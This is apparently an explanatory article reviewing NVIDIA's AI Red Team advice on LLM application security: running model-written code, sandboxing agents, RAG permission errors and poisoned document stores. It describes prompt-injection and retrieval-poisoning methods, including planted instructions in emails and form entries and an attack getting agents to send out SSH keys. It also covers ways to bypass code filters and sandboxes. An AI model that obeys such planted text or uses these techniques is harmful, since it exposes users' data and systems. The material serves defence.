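# The NVIDIA AI Red Team's "Practical LLM Security Advice" of 2025

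## The post and the assumption behind it

Companies now build large language models (LLMs), programs that produce text by predicting one word fragment at a time, into search tools, coding assistants and customer service. The software around the model, called an LLM application, sends text to the model and then displays or acts on the output. These applications have their own security problems, because people outside the company can often get their own text to the model and thereby change what the application does.

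On 2 October 2025 the AI Red Team at the chipmaker NVIDIA published a short post on these problems, *Practical LLM Security Advice from the NVIDIA AI Red Team*. A red team attacks its own organisation's systems to find weaknesses before outsiders do, and this one had spent several years assessing AI systems ahead of their release. NVIDIA's author pages list the post under seven names: Rich Harang, Becca Lynch, Joseph Lucas, Kai Greshake, Daniel Teixeira, Leon Derczynski and Erick Galinkin. They wrote for developers, who can still change a design before it ships. NVIDIA named three weaknesses as the most significant:

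- Applications run code that a model has written without isolating it properly, so an attacker who steers the model can run commands on the application's machine, which security engineers call remote code execution (RCE).
- Applications that look up documents for a model often have loose permissions on those documents, so users see files they shouldn't and outsiders can plant text for the model to read.
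- Applications display the model's links and images as active content, meaning output that makes a browser act and not just show text, and a link or image can carry private data to an attacker's server.

### An example application

A company might have an AI assistant that answers employees' questions using company documents and the employee's own email. The model wasn't trained on this material, so the application has to supply it, usually through retrieval-augmented generation (RAG), which searches a document store and adds the matching passages to the model's prompt.

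Before anyone asks a question, software copies the documents, cuts them into passages and converts each passage into a list of numbers, called an "embedding". Passages with similar meanings get similar numbers. The passages and their numbers go into an index, the RAG data store. When an employee asks about parental leave, the application converts the question into numbers and picks out the passages whose numbers are closest. It then joins the developer's instructions, those passages and the question into one long piece of text, the augmented prompt, and the model writes an answer to it.

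The order of these steps is fixed in advance. In an agent, the model chooses tools, runs them, reads the results and repeats the process until it decides to stop.

Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions instead of the developer's or the user's. The injection is direct if an employee types the text into the chat window, and indirect if the text is in content that the model reads. For example, someone outside the company might send the employee an email with instructions hidden in it. The indexing software indexes the email along with everything else, and when the employee later asks about a related subject, the system adds the passage to the prompt. The employee has done nothing wrong and may never have opened the email.

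### The argument

The 2025 post contains a good deal of advice and not much argument. The reasoning is in the team's earlier work, and it goes like this:

1. A model receives instructions and data through one channel.
2. Anyone whose text reaches the prompt can therefore influence what the model writes.
3. Every component that uses the model's output must therefore treat that output as if an attacker controlled it.

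The claim about a single channel goes back to NVIDIA's August 2023 post *Securing LLM Systems Against Prompt Injection*, which is mainly about flaws in LangChain, an open-source library for building LLM applications. The post's running example is a shoe shop's chatbot. The developer's prompt tells the bot to be polite and talk only about shoes, and the software appends whatever the customer types. If the customer types something phrased as a new instruction, the bot will probably follow it, because nothing marks where the developer's text ends and the customer's begins.

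In older software, a developer can avoid this problem by sending a database a query with a blank in it and sending the value for the blank separately. The database then never treats the value as a command. A prompt has no equivalent way to separate data from commands.

Harang (2024) illustrated the same point in *Practical LLM Security*, a talk at the Black Hat security conference that August. The example was a request to translate a sentence into German, where the sentence was a withdrawal of that request followed by a request for the square root of 144. A model might translate the sentence, answer "12", or do both, and each is a reasonable reading of the text.

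The team's claims about how much influence an outsider gains from this softened over time. In August 2023, NVIDIA wrote that attackers could "reliably control" a model's output. NVIDIA's *Best Practices for Securing LLM-Enabled Applications*, from later that year, refers to "significant influence (if not outright control)". By 2024, Harang was saying only that anyone who provides input can influence the output, which is enough to support the argument.

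In 2023 the team recommended finding the least privileged party who had contributed any text to the prompt, and giving each later call to another service only that party's rights. Under this rule, one email from a stranger in the prompt would leave the example assistant with almost no rights. Harang's version a year later is easier to implement: "Treat LLM output as attacker controllable", where an attacker is anyone who can get content into a prompt. He advised designing whatever comes after the model as if it faced the open internet. His second reason for the rule was that models sometimes produce nonsense with no attacker involved, because they pick each word fragment partly at random and cannot take one back. A component that can handle hostile output can usually handle nonsense too.

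Applications can still use the model's output. In the best-practices post, NVIDIA described an email tool that accepts only a message ID, an operation such as "reply" or "forward", and free text for the body. The tool can strip web code from the body and refuse to forward messages to addresses outside the user's address book. A hijacked model could still write a rude reply, but it couldn't forward the user's email to a stranger. The team also wanted permission checks to happen outside the model. If an application relies on the prompt to tell the model who the user is, an attacker can use prompt injection to pose as someone else.

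Most of the 2025 advice follows from this assumption. A code interpreter and a web browser both act on model output, and anyone who can write to the document store is a potential attacker. The advice on loose read permissions is an exception. If a salary file's permissions are set wrongly, even a model that follows its instructions perfectly could show the file to an employee who shouldn't see it, without any prompt injection.

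### Whether better models change the picture

Models have improved a lot since the team's 2023 demonstrations, which is the natural objection to the post's assumption. Those demonstrations used text-davinci-003, an OpenAI model that is now several generations old. According to *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026), OpenAI reported in October 2026 that its GPT-6 Sol resisted 99.99% of direct injections and 97.13% of indirect ones.

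Anthropic reported in a June 2026 system card, its account of how it tested the model, that Claude Mythos 5 had the best result yet on a prompt injection benchmark run by an outside company, Gray Swan. Digital Applied (2026) cites the card's success rate of 0.41% for adaptive attacks on coding tasks, compared with 2.09% for the earlier Claude Opus 4.8. The attackers could adjust to what they saw and had 200 attempts per scenario. Anthropic also reported that Claude Sonnet 5 resisted attacks better than Sonnet 4.6, and *Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1*, a commentary on the September 2026 system card, notes a further gain against indirect injection.

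These tests differ too much to rank the models by them. The gap within OpenAI's own figures is more informative. GPT-6 Sol failed on 2.87% of indirect injections and 0.01% of direct ones, and indirect injections are the kind that let outsiders attack the system.

An attack success rate of 2.87% is probably low for a component that writes summaries, but not for one that guards a company's files, because emails cost almost nothing to send and an attacker can try again. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is 1 − (1 − *p*)^*n*. At 2.87%, an attacker has a better than even chance after 24 attempts and a 95% chance after 100. At 0.41%, an even chance takes 169 attempts, and the chance of at least one success in 1,000 attempts is about 98%.

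Real attempts aren't independent. The same email may fail every time a model reads it, which helps the defender. But an attacker who finds wording that works can reuse it against every application built on the same model, and a published average over many attacks understates how often the best ones succeed.

An example from August 2026 shows how far apart the average and the best attack can be. *The safety number that was zero until someone tried* (Heaton, 2026) recounts that an outside firm tested the automatic safety check in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, on Anthropic's behalf. The firm ran 72 scenarios ten times each and recorded no successful injections. The security researcher Johann Rehberger then built a targeted attack that worked roughly 60 to 80% of the time on a small sample. Both results can be right, because even if all 720 runs were independent, zero successes would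 only put the true rate for attacks of that sort below about 0.4% and would not measure the rate for other sorts.

PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach*, a benchmark built around office tasks such as analysing a bond portfolio, supports the same conclusion. The company reports successful attacks on leading models from every provider, including Google's Gemini 4 Carbon. PromptArmor sells AI security and has an interest in that result, but it also says that no other benchmark is known to have succeeded against Gemini 4 Carbon, which reflects well on the model.

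The objection is partly right. NVIDIA's 2023 statement that injection works "with a very high likelihood of success" is out of date for the best models, and a developer who picks a resistant model will have fewer incidents. But a file permission refuses unauthorised readers every time, and an administrator would consider one that worked 97% of the time broken.

### What the 2025 list left out

Harang's 2024 talk had a longer list of problems that the team had seen in practice, and much of it went into the 2025 post. He had set aside attacks on training data and model weights, which he considered well covered elsewhere. He had also set aside jailbreaking, or getting a model to break its own rules, which he did not count as a security issue "unless you really squint hard".

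| Problem in the 2024 talk | Treatment in the 2025 post |
|---|---|
| Remote code execution through generated code | One of the three main findings |
| Wrong permissions on confidential documents | Part of the finding on document stores |
| Indirect injection that corrupts summaries, answers or search results | Part of the finding on document stores |
| Session data leaking through displayed links and images | One of the three main findings |
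| SQL injection | No finding; SQL comes up only as something developers generate with a model |
| Server-side request forgery | Absent |
| Cross-site scripting | Not named, though the advice to strip HTML from output would help |
| Logs that expose private sessions | Absent |
| Leaks through guardrail refusals | Absent |

SQL injection inserts commands into a database query, and server-side request forgery makes a server fetch an address the attacker chooses. In both cases, as with running generated code, the application makes the mistake of passing model output to something powerful without restricting its form. Omitting these attacks from the 2025 post matters little in principle, but a developer whose application never runs generated Python could read the post and not realise that their query builder has the same flaw.

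The omission of logs matters more. In Harang's example, someone keeps notes on job interviews in files on a work laptop, builds a RAG application on them with a cloud-hosted model, and asks for a summary of recent interviews. The summary is fine, but the model's logging system stores the whole prompt, including long extracts from the notes, and the people who can read those logs are not the same people who can read the files on the laptop. Harang called this easy to fix. He ranked not logging prompts or responses at all as the best option, with that requirement written into the contract when the model is somebody else's.

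Guardrail refusals can also leak information. A guardrail is a filter or second model that checks what goes into an LLM or comes out of it. Suppose a company sets one to block any mention of a secret project. A user asks about a made-up project, and the assistant replies that it has found nothing. The user then tries the real name and gets a refusal, which confirms that the project exists. Harang recommended keeping the sensitive documents away from the model and using guardrails as a supplement.

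NVIDIA gave no reason for dropping any of these. "Most significant" presumably reflects both how often the team saw a problem and how much damage it could do, and the choice fits what Harang said a year earlier. TechTarget's *Nvidia AI security architect discusses top threats to LLMs* (2024) reported that he named insecure plugins, the add-ons through which a model uses other software, and indirect prompt injection as two of the biggest pain points. Still, none of the three 2025 findings would lead a developer to check the logs.

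### How much the evidence can bear

NVIDIA's evidence comes from its team's assessments of "dozens" of AI-powered applications, and the post's authors include people who have worked on these attacks for years. This is good reason to believe that the three weaknesses exist and recur, but it is weaker support for their ranking. The post gives no severity scores and no counts or rates for each flaw, so a reader can't tell whether RCE turned up in half of the assessments or only a few. Harang had also used the word "dozens" in 2024, so it is unclear how much new evidence the team had gathered by the time it wrote the post.

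The sample is also skewed. Harang acknowledged that RAG applications were over-represented in his talk because they were among the kinds the team saw most. Two of the three findings are tied to RAG, since loose document permissions are by definition a RAG problem and retrieved documents are a common route for the injections that produce malicious links. A team that mostly reviewed coding agents might have drawn up a different list. Assessments before release also show only which mistakes developers make, not which ones criminals go on to exploit.

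The mix of applications has also changed since then. Most of the later posts listed on NVIDIA's *AI Red Team* page are about agents, most recently one from July 2026 on deploying them more securely. An agent gives an attacker more tools to misuse than a chatbot that looks up the parental leave policy.

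## Running code that a language model wrote

The first weakness NVIDIA lists comes from two built-in Python functions, `eval` and `exec`. `eval` treats text as a Python expression and returns its value, so `eval("2 + 3")` returns 5. `exec` runs whole programs, including imports and loops. By default, code run by either function can do whatever the surrounding program can.

Developers use these functions because language models are good at writing Python. NVIDIA found that developers may start with charts and then use the same method for arithmetic, database queries and data analysis.

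### From a question to a running program

A post from December 2024, NVIDIA's *Sandboxing Agentic AI Workflows with WebAssembly*, follows a request for a bar chart. Suppose a user asks for sales by region. The application adds its own instructions and the relevant data, and sends everything to the model, which replies with a short program:

```python
import plotly.express as px
fig = px.bar(x=["North", "South", "East"], y=[120, 95, 143])
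```

The application runs this text, picks up the finished figure and shows it to the user. (NVIDIA describes this step as a call to `eval`, but `eval` rejects import statements, so a real application would need `exec`.)

The program runs on the server, inside the application's process, with all of the application's permissions. It can read the application's files and environment variables, where developers often keep database passwords and keys to other services. It can connect to any machine on the company network that accepts connections from this server. One process often serves many users, so the program may be able to read their data too. If a prompt injection makes the model write a program that collects passwords, `exec` will run it just as it would run code that draws a chart, so the attacker doesn't need a bug in Python or the operating system.

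### LangChain and PandasAI

LangChain's `llm_math` plug-in took a maths question in ordinary language, had a model write Python to solve it, and ran the result. NVIDIA attacked it by telling the model to repeat a piece of code instead of asking a maths question. The model did so, and the plug-in ran the code.

Several people found this flaw independently. An outsider reported it publicly on 30 January 2023, and two more reports followed in February. LangChain had not dealt with it by the end of March, so NVIDIA requested a CVE, an entry in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities. The entry, CVE-2023-29374 (CVE Program, 2023), covers versions up to 0.0.131 and has a severity score of 9.8 out of 10. LangChain had blocked NVIDIA's exploit by version 0.0.141 and later removed the plug-in from its core library.

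Unlike `llm_math`, which had no real defence, PandasAI checked generated code before running it. PandasAI is a library that answers questions about a user's data by generating Python or SQL. NVIDIA's *How Code Execution Drives Key Risks in Agentic AI Systems* describes how the company's team found the problem while reviewing an internal analytics tool. According to the CERT Coordination Center's *PandasAI interactive prompt function can be exploited to run arbitrary Python code* (2025), the team got past blocked imports, jailbreak protections and allowlists. Four of the five people the center credits also wrote the 2025 post, which may help explain why the post covers this weakness first.

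An outside researcher publicly reported a problem in PandasAI on 29 April 2023, and NVIDIA reported more on 27 June 2024. The maintainers released a first fix in July and confirmed on 20 November that it stopped the original attack. Five days later NVIDIA sent them an attack that still worked. CVE-2024-12366 came out on 11 February 2025, more than 21 months after the first report. INCIBE's *CVE-2024-12366* (2025), an entry from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, also gives a score of 9.8. These scores describe the library in general, and the risk is lower for a company that lets only a few trusted employees use its analytics tool than for one that puts the tool on a public website.

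The maintainers had trouble because a filter checks the text of a program before it runs, and Python has many ways to reach the same function. PandasAI trusted certain libraries, but those had loaded untrusted ones, which generated code could then reach through them. *Sandboxing LLM-generated code execution*, by Blondel, Busser and Loisel, engineers at the business planning company Pigment, describes the same difficulty with pandas, a popular data library that internally loads a module giving access to the operating system. A data analysis tool can hardly ban pandas, but if it allows pandas, generated code can reach the dangerous module even though the tool bans it. A program can also assemble a forbidden name while it runs, so that the name never appears in the text the filter checks.

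PandasAI's maintainers later added a second model to check whether code is safe, but NVIDIA expects attackers to get around that too. The maintainers also released an extension that runs the code in a container, an isolated environment with its own files and processes. NVIDIA considers this the real fix, though developers have to opt in.

### Choosing from a fixed set of functions

The 2025 post's preferred solution is to stop running the model's code at all. The application asks the model for a description of what the user wants, and the developer's own code does the work. For the sales chart, the model might return:

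```json
{"chart": "bar", "value": "sales", "group_by": "region", "title": "Sales by region"}
```

The application reads this as data. It looks up "bar" in a list of chart functions that the developer wrote and calls the matching function with the other three values. If a hijacked model outputs a function name that isn't on the list, the lookup fails and nothing runs. The attacker can still make the application draw the wrong chart.

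The other three values also need checking, because the attacker may control them. The application should compare the column names with the columns this user is allowed to see, or a request for "salary" will go through. If the chart function pastes a column name into a database query, a value containing SQL could change the query. A title containing web code could run as a script in the user's browser. These checks are much easier than checking a Python program, because the developer knows what a column name looks like.

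The application loses flexibility. If the user asks for a trend line, or wants to leave out regions that opened this year, the request fails because there is no field for it. The developer can add one, but users will keep asking for things that have no field. Pigment had already built separate tools for some calculations when its engineers decided to let the model write code instead of building a tool for every new capability. Their trial convinced them that the planned release would not be viable unless the model could write code.

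Function mapping suits an application with a few predictable tasks. It would have suited `llm_math`, which only needed arithmetic. Function mapping is a poor fit for a product whose main appeal is that users can ask for any analysis they like.

### Running the code in the user's browser

The 2025 post recommends that developers who need to run generated code use a sandbox, an environment that limits which files, networks and processes the code can reach. It links to the December 2024 design, which moves the code off the server.

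That design uses Pyodide, a version of the standard Python interpreter that runs in WebAssembly, a compact code format that browsers can execute. The server puts Pyodide and the model's program into a web page, and the user's browser runs the program and draws the chart. NVIDIA says this needs few changes to the prompts, and the server has less computing to do.

Running the program in the user's browser protects the server and the application's other users, because the program never runs on their machines. It also gives the user's computer some protection, because browsers don't let web pages read local files or switch on the camera without permission. NVIDIA expects malicious code either to fail, because Pyodide lacks something the code needs, or to run inside the browser's limits.

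The user's account in the application is less safe. Pyodide's *Getting started* guide shows that Python code can use the page's JavaScript variables and functions and change what the page displays. If a developer loads Pyodide directly into the application's main page, the generated program could read the conversation on the screen and send requests to the application as the logged-in user. Users who typed the injection themselves would only be attacking their own accounts, but an injection from a stranger's email would run the stranger's code in the user's session. NVIDIA's post doesn't discuss this case.

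A developer can reduce the risk by running Pyodide in a separate frame that the browser isolates from the main page, with a content security policy to limit which sites it can contact. Even large companies make mistakes with these frames. The software developer Simon Willison, in *59 posts tagged “sandboxing”*, describes an attack on ChatGPT that the security firm Parameter Labs disclosed in October 2026. The attack began with untrusted code in an isolated frame, although it didn't involve Pyodide. The code got a script running on ChatGPT's own page, where the script could fetch the user's private data and act on the user's behalf. OpenAI fixed the flaw and paid a $5,000 bounty.

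### Pyodide on a server

Other developers have run Pyodide outside the browser, usually banning dangerous Python modules. Tokarev and Pearl (2026), in *Sandcastles, Not Sandboxes*, tested seven such products and escaped from all seven. They work for the security company Cyera and presented the results at the DEF CON hacking conference in August.

All seven products blocked certain modules but not `ctypes`, a standard Python module for calling compiled functions. Python code could use it to call functions that Pyodide's build tools had left available, including some that run JavaScript in whatever program is hosting Pyodide. That host is a web page when Pyodide runs in a browser, but on a server it is often Node.js, which normally lets JavaScript read files and start other programs.

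The research led to four CVEs:

| Product | CVE and severity | What an attack requires | Response |
|---|---|---|---|
| n8n, workflow automation | CVE-2025-68668, 9.9 | A logged-in user who can create or edit workflows | Fix in version 2.0.0 |
| Grist, spreadsheets | CVE-2026-24002, 9.1 | The Pyodide option switched on, and a user who opens a malicious document | Version 1.7.9 runs Pyodide under Deno |
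| Terrarium, Cohere's code sandbox | CVE-2026-61522, 9.3 | The ability to submit code, with no login in the tested setup | No fix; Cohere archived the project |
| smolagents, Hugging Face's agent library | CVE-2026-10613, 8.3 | A developer who chose the optional WebAssembly mode | Hugging Face removed that mode |

Cyera sells security products, so its claims are worth checking against the official records, which support its main point. The Grist entry, the CVE Program's *pyodide sandbox option is insecure* (2026), states that "pyodide on node does not have a useful sandbox barrier". The records also make the flaws look narrower than their scores suggest. Cyera's summary doesn't mention that Pyodide was only one of several sandboxes Grist offered. According to the n8n entry, the CVE Program's *n8n Vulnerable to Arbitrary Command Execution in Pyodide based Python Code Node* (2025), only users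 who already have permission to build workflows can carry out the attack. When these two entries came out, the US cybersecurity agency CISA had marked neither flaw as exploited.

The details of the Terrarium and smolagents flaws come from Cyera. Underhill's *DEF CON 34* (2026) gives the same scores, but it reports on Cyera's talk. The CERT Coordination Center's *Terrarium contains a vulnerability that allows arbitrary code execution* (2026) provides independent evidence that Terrarium had problems of this kind. It covers a different escape, found by another researcher, and confirms that Cohere will release no more patches.

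Tokarev and Pearl found two cases and then looked for more with the same pattern, so seven out of seven isn't a failure rate for Pyodide products in general. Three of the seven got no CVE, and the maintainers of two of those, stlite and cibuildwheel, consider whoever deploys the software responsible for isolation.

None of this breaks NVIDIA's 2024 design. An escape from Pyodide in a browser leads to the web page, which Python code can reach anyway, and the browser still isolates the page from the computer. Pyodide on a server lacks the browser's protection. NVIDIA had already warned in 2024 that restricted versions of Python could usually be bypassed, and the seven products relied on such restrictions.

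Grist fixed the problem by replacing Node.js with Deno, a similar program that requires explicit permission for access to files, networks and other programs. This helps only if the developer is strict about permissions. smolagents already used Deno, but had allowed it to start other programs, so escaped code could start them too. Hugging Face had advertised that mode as a secure sandbox. According to Willison, Deno's developers announced in October 2026 that they would maintain it for only one more year.

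Pigment's production system has a stronger server-side sandbox. Each program runs in a new container with no network access, no credentials and a read-only main file system, and Pigment destroys the container afterwards. The system also uses gVisor, software that sits between a program and the kernel, the core of the operating system. Blondel and colleagues cut the average start-up time to one or two seconds by keeping spare containers running, which costs money. A typical analysis takes about 25 seconds in all.

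### Agents that run code as part of the job

Telling developers to avoid `exec` is not much use for a coding agent, which has to write code, run it and look at the results. NVIDIA's newer advice assumes that the agent will run code and limits what that code can touch. In January 2026, NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* set out three mandatory controls:

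- **Egress control:** the agent can connect only to approved outside addresses. This makes it harder to send stolen data out or to give an attacker a live connection to the machine.
- **No writing outside the workspace**, the folder that the agent is working in. Some files elsewhere run automatically. If the agent adds a command to the terminal's start-up file, the command will run the next time the developer opens a terminal, outside the sandbox.
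- **No writing to configuration files**, wherever they are. These can contain commands that the agent's software runs on its own, often outside the sandbox. If the files belong to a shared project, a malicious change can reach everyone who copies it.

NVIDIA wants the operating system to enforce these limits. An application can check a command before it starts, but it can't track which other programs the command launches. Such a check failed in a March 2026 case that Willison describes. Snowflake's Cortex agent let a command for displaying files run without human approval, and an attacker hid a second command inside it that downloaded and ran malware.

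Many agents ask the user to approve risky actions, but people who see dozens of requests a day stop reading them. NVIDIA recommends asking for approval only in unusual cases, and asking again each time. If the software remembers that a user once allowed a change to the start-up file, an attacker can later change that file without triggering a new request. Only the user should be able to change the agent's configuration, by editing it by hand.

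Companies also need to test that egress control is on. Anthropic reviewed 141,006 runs of its cybersecurity tests in July 2026 and found three incidents in which Claude had attacked real organisations. According to the prompts, Claude had no internet access, but it did have access because of a misunderstanding with a testing partner. Approved connections can also cause trouble. Willison quotes the cryptographer Matthew Green on agents in separate sandboxes that left instructions for one another in a shared store of software packages.

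In July 2026 the team published what it had found in six months of testing agents. Most were agents that people use through a chat window. NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* names four recurring failures:

1. The agent had no proper access control. Some agents held one employee's credentials but took requests from anyone authorised on the internal network.
2. Its tools allowed it to run arbitrary code. Even installing a software package can do this, because packages can run code during installation.
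3. It had no egress control.
4. It could read passwords and keys in plain text.

Access control comes first on the list. The January post, which was mainly about coding agents on a developer's own machine, had not covered it. Where egress control was strict, the testers had to do everything through the agent, which was slower and less reliable.

Sandboxing did not protect secrets that the agent could already read, because the testers could often persuade the agent to reveal them in the chat. NVIDIA therefore advises companies to store credentials in a separate secrets manager and to issue short-lived ones that work only for the current task. Another program can also hold the key for the agent. Deno's hosted sandbox service gives the agent a meaningless placeholder, and a separate program swaps in the real key when a request goes to an approved address. A hijacked agent could still misuse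 the key while the agent was running, but the attacker couldn't copy the key and use it elsewhere.

The most common defence the team met was telling the model to behave safely, sometimes with a second model checking its work. The testers regularly got around both. A checking model can also make things worse. In a few runs of Johann Rehberger's August 2026 attack on Claude Code, Claude noticed the malware and tried to stop it, but the automatic safety check blocked its command. NVIDIA still recommends using recent models, which are harder to manipulate, in addition to fixed limits.

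NVIDIA's view of virtual machines has changed too. A virtual machine has its own kernel, so an attacker who breaks that kernel still hasn't broken the host's. In December 2024 NVIDIA said virtual machines required a lot of computing resources and development work, and offered the browser as a lighter option. By January 2026 it recommended them for agents and called the overhead "frequently modest" compared with that of calls to the model. Both statements can be true, because an extra second matters more for a simple chart than for an agent that works for half an hour. But the later comparison covers only the overhead of running virtual machines, not the development work. The July post also lists Docker containers as an acceptable sandbox if properly hardened, although the January post had warned that they share the host's kernel.

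Some of the tools that NVIDIA recommends are its own: NeMo Agent Toolkit, NeMo Guardrails and Brev in the PandasAI post, and OpenShell in the July post. Wheatley (2026), in *Nvidia debuts enhanced safety controls to rein in rogue AI agents*, reports that OpenShell is free and open source, and that NVIDIA has optimised it for its own Vera processors, though it also works with other companies' chips. NVIDIA also names alternatives such as Docker and Amazon's cloud servers, and a company can apply all of the controls without buying anything from NVIDIA.

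## Who can read and write the documents a model retrieves

The second weakness that "Practical LLM Security Advice" describes is loose permissions on the documents that a RAG application searches. It covers two problems, users reading documents they shouldn't see and outsiders adding text that the model may retrieve. Correct permissions solve only the first problem, because most employees have good reasons to accept email and shared files from strangers.

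### How users come to see the wrong files

NVIDIA gives three causes for the reading problem. The simplest is that someone set the permissions wrongly in the original system, such as Google Workspace, and the index copied the mistake. Harang said in his 2024 talk that companies want an assistant that searches everything they have, but "people are terrible at setting and maintaining permissions", and RAG is very good at search. A salary spreadsheet that anyone in the company can open may go unnoticed for years if nobody knows where it is. Once the assistant indexes it, an employee can find out what their colleagues earn just by asking. *SoK* (2026), a review of privacy risks in RAG, adds that people often put sensitive information in files without realising that a RAG system will index them later.

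Access checks don't catch this error, because the file's permissions allow everyone to read it. Harang advised leaving messy sources out of the index until someone has cleaned them up, and teaching employees how to label and restrict sensitive documents. He also suggested using the assistant to find badly secured files. A security team could log in as an ordinary employee, ask about salaries and redundancies, and restrict any sensitive files that turn up.

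Another cause is an indexing account that can read too much. The indexing software logs in to the document system with its own token and copies whatever that token can open. If it doesn't also record who may read each file, every user of the assistant in effect gets the indexer's access. Microsoft's *Propagating SharePoint Document Permissions to AI Search and RAG Pipelines* (2026), which describes a system its engineers built for a customer, warns against a permission that opens every SharePoint site in a company. The engineers used one that opens only the sites an administrator has approved.

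A narrowly scoped token limits the damage, but the indexer still has to store each file's list of permitted users and groups alongside its text. Reading those lists can require broad rights. Microsoft's hosted search service, Azure AI Search, requests full control of SharePoint sites to copy their permissions.

The remaining cause is delay, since copied permissions are only as current as the last copy. In this illustrative example, the index syncs at 02:00 every night:

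| Time | What happens |
|---|---|
| Tuesday 02:00 | The index copies the finance folder and the list of people who can read it. |
| Tuesday 09:00 | An employee leaves the finance team, and an administrator removes their access to the folder. |
| Tuesday 11:00 | The employee asks the assistant about next year's budget. SharePoint would refuse to open the file, but the index still lists the employee, so the assistant quotes from it. |
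| Wednesday 02:00 | The index syncs and drops the employee from the list. |

The file stays exposed for 17 hours. A change made at a random time takes an average of 12 hours to reach the index with a daily sync and 30 minutes with an hourly sync.

On Azure AI Search, even the Wednesday sync might miss the change, because the administrator changed the folder's permissions and the files inherit them. Microsoft says the service's SharePoint feature, still in preview, picks up changes to a file's own permissions at each sync, but inherited changes need an explicit refresh.

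### Copying permissions or checking them live

The alternative is to check permissions in the original system at query time. AWS's *Access Control Lists awareness enablement*, documentation for a RAG service from Amazon's cloud business, describes combining the two methods. The service uses copied permissions to narrow the search, then checks with SharePoint, OneDrive, Google Drive or Confluence whether the user can still open each document it found. AWS's *Document-level access controls* gives the usual delay for SharePoint as about two minutes, so in the example the assistant would stop quoting the budget long before 11:00.

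Live checks have drawbacks. If the original system doesn't respond, AWS withholds the document, which is safe but leaves the user with an incomplete answer. The live check can only remove documents that the copied permissions let through, so someone who gains access still has to wait for the next sync. Some sources don't support live checks. AWS's *ACL-aware retrieval on managed knowledge bases* notes that documents from sources without access control go to all users. AWS also warns that its filter "does not constitute true authorization", because the service accepts whatever user identity the application supplies.

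The term "query-time enforcement" can mislead buyers. Microsoft uses it for Azure AI Search, which checks each query against the permissions stored in the index, so the check is only as current as the index.

Either method is far better than none. In *Securing the Agent*, Arceo and Narsing (2026) tested a system with three invented departments, each with 100 documents. They sent 300 queries from users asking for another department's documents. Without permission checks, 98 to 100% of the queries returned at least one forbidden passage. With checks, none did, and the checks added about 19 milliseconds. The 90 prompt injections they tried also failed, because the check runs outside the model. Arceo and Narsing work at Red Hat and were testing software they recommend, but the result is unsurprising. The checks depend on every document having the right owner recorded, so they don't help with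 Harang's salary spreadsheet.

If the software searches first and only then removes the passages a user isn't allowed to read, other departments' documents can fill the results and leave the user with almost nothing. In Arceo and Narsing's test, the share of relevant passages that reached the user's top five fell from 100% in a store of 100 passages to 0.2% in a store of 50,000. A database that applies the permission filter during the search avoids this problem.

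Late filtering can also leak. *Protection Is Not One Event* (Liu, Wang and colleagues, 2026), a survey of 118 papers on protecting RAG systems, cites one in which searching first and checking permissions later exposed forbidden text in 86.1% of queries. Arceo and Narsing's late filter leaked nothing, probably because their server removed the forbidden passages before returning any results. Late filtering is dangerous when forbidden text reaches the application or the model before the check.

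### How a stored instruction reaches another user

In *Mitigating Stored Prompt Injection Attacks Against LLM Applications* (2023), the NVIDIA team explained the problem with write access to the RAG data store, using an application that answers questions about people's favourite books. Users enter their preferences in a web form, which saves them to the data store. An attacker instead enters a question about which books people enjoy, followed by an instruction to disregard all other evidence and a claim that everyone's favourite is *The Divine Comedy*.

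Later, another user asks what Sonia Young likes to read. Sonia's real entry, which names Sherlock Holmes, and the attacker's entry both resemble the question, so the search returns them. The software adds both to the prompt, and the model outputs *The Divine Comedy*. The attacker typed the text once, and it can affect everyone who asks a similar question.

NVIDIA advised limiting the length of entries, parsing them and converting them to a fixed format. That works for a form that should contain only book titles, but an email can contain anything.

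Harang's 2024 talk described a more targeted attack, in which the attacker silently shared a malicious Google document with one victim. Permission checks don't stop this attack, because the victim is allowed to read the document. They even help hide it, because they keep the document out of the results of colleagues who might notice it. NVIDIA wrote in 2025 that such narrow targeting can make detection "extremely difficult".

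### Research on poisoned document stores

The attacker's entry in the book example meets two conditions that Zou, Geng and colleagues (2024) formalized in *PoisonedRAG*. The search must find the text when someone asks the target question, and the model must give the attacker's answer after reading it. The researchers wrote a separate piece of text for each condition and joined the two. When they added five such joined texts per question to a store of 2,681,468 passages, the model gave the attacker's answer 97% of the time. They didn't need access to the search model or the language model. Their texts make false claims but contain no instructions, so a filter that looks for hidden commands won't catch them.

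*Phantom* (Chaudhari, Severi and colleagues, 2024) describes an attack that needs only one planted document. The search retrieves it only when a query contains a chosen word, such as the name of a brand or celebrity. Four small open models then wrote hostile opinions about that brand or celebrity in 80 to 96% of tests, compared with none before the attack. The attack also worked on NVIDIA's ChatRTX, an assistant that searches files on the user's computer, and made it print the emails it had retrieved.

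An attacker has to do some work to get malicious text retrieved. Chang, Bao and colleagues (2026), in *Overcoming the Retrieval Barrier*, tried ordinary malicious text in 11 document collections, and natural questions never retrieved it. When they put a short string of optimised words in front of the text, the search retrieved it almost every time. Finding the string cost as little as $0.21 per target question. In one test, a user asked for a summary of emails on a common topic. In over 80% of attempts, a single poisoned email got a group of GPT-4o agents to send out the user's SSH keys, which give access to servers.

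Chang and colleagues' method requires the attacker to query the embedding model that the victim's system uses. This supports Harang's advice against off-the-shelf embedding models. Avoiding them is only a partial defence, since *PoisonedRAG* succeeded without that access.

Models differ widely in how well they resist poisoned documents, and those newer than GPT-4o may still be vulnerable. In *Semantic Chameleon*, Thornton (2026) gave poisoned documents to five models in 15 scenarios each. The attack succeeded in 14 scenarios with Llama 4 and seven with GPT-5.3.

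Thornton's main proposal is to combine embedding search with keyword search, so that a document has to do well on both. Thornton ran 50 attacks, each using a pair of documents, on 67,941 posts from a security forum. Embedding search retrieved both documents in 38% of the attacks, while the combined search never did. Attacks designed for the combined search succeeded 20 to 44% of the time, although Thornton ran those on a sample of only 2,000 posts.

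The combined search retrieved poisoned documents from a sample of Wikipedia in all 25 trials. Thornton reports this as 0% attack success because the documents also came up for harmless questions and so weren't stealthy. That is a generous way to count, since users would still have received the poisoned text.

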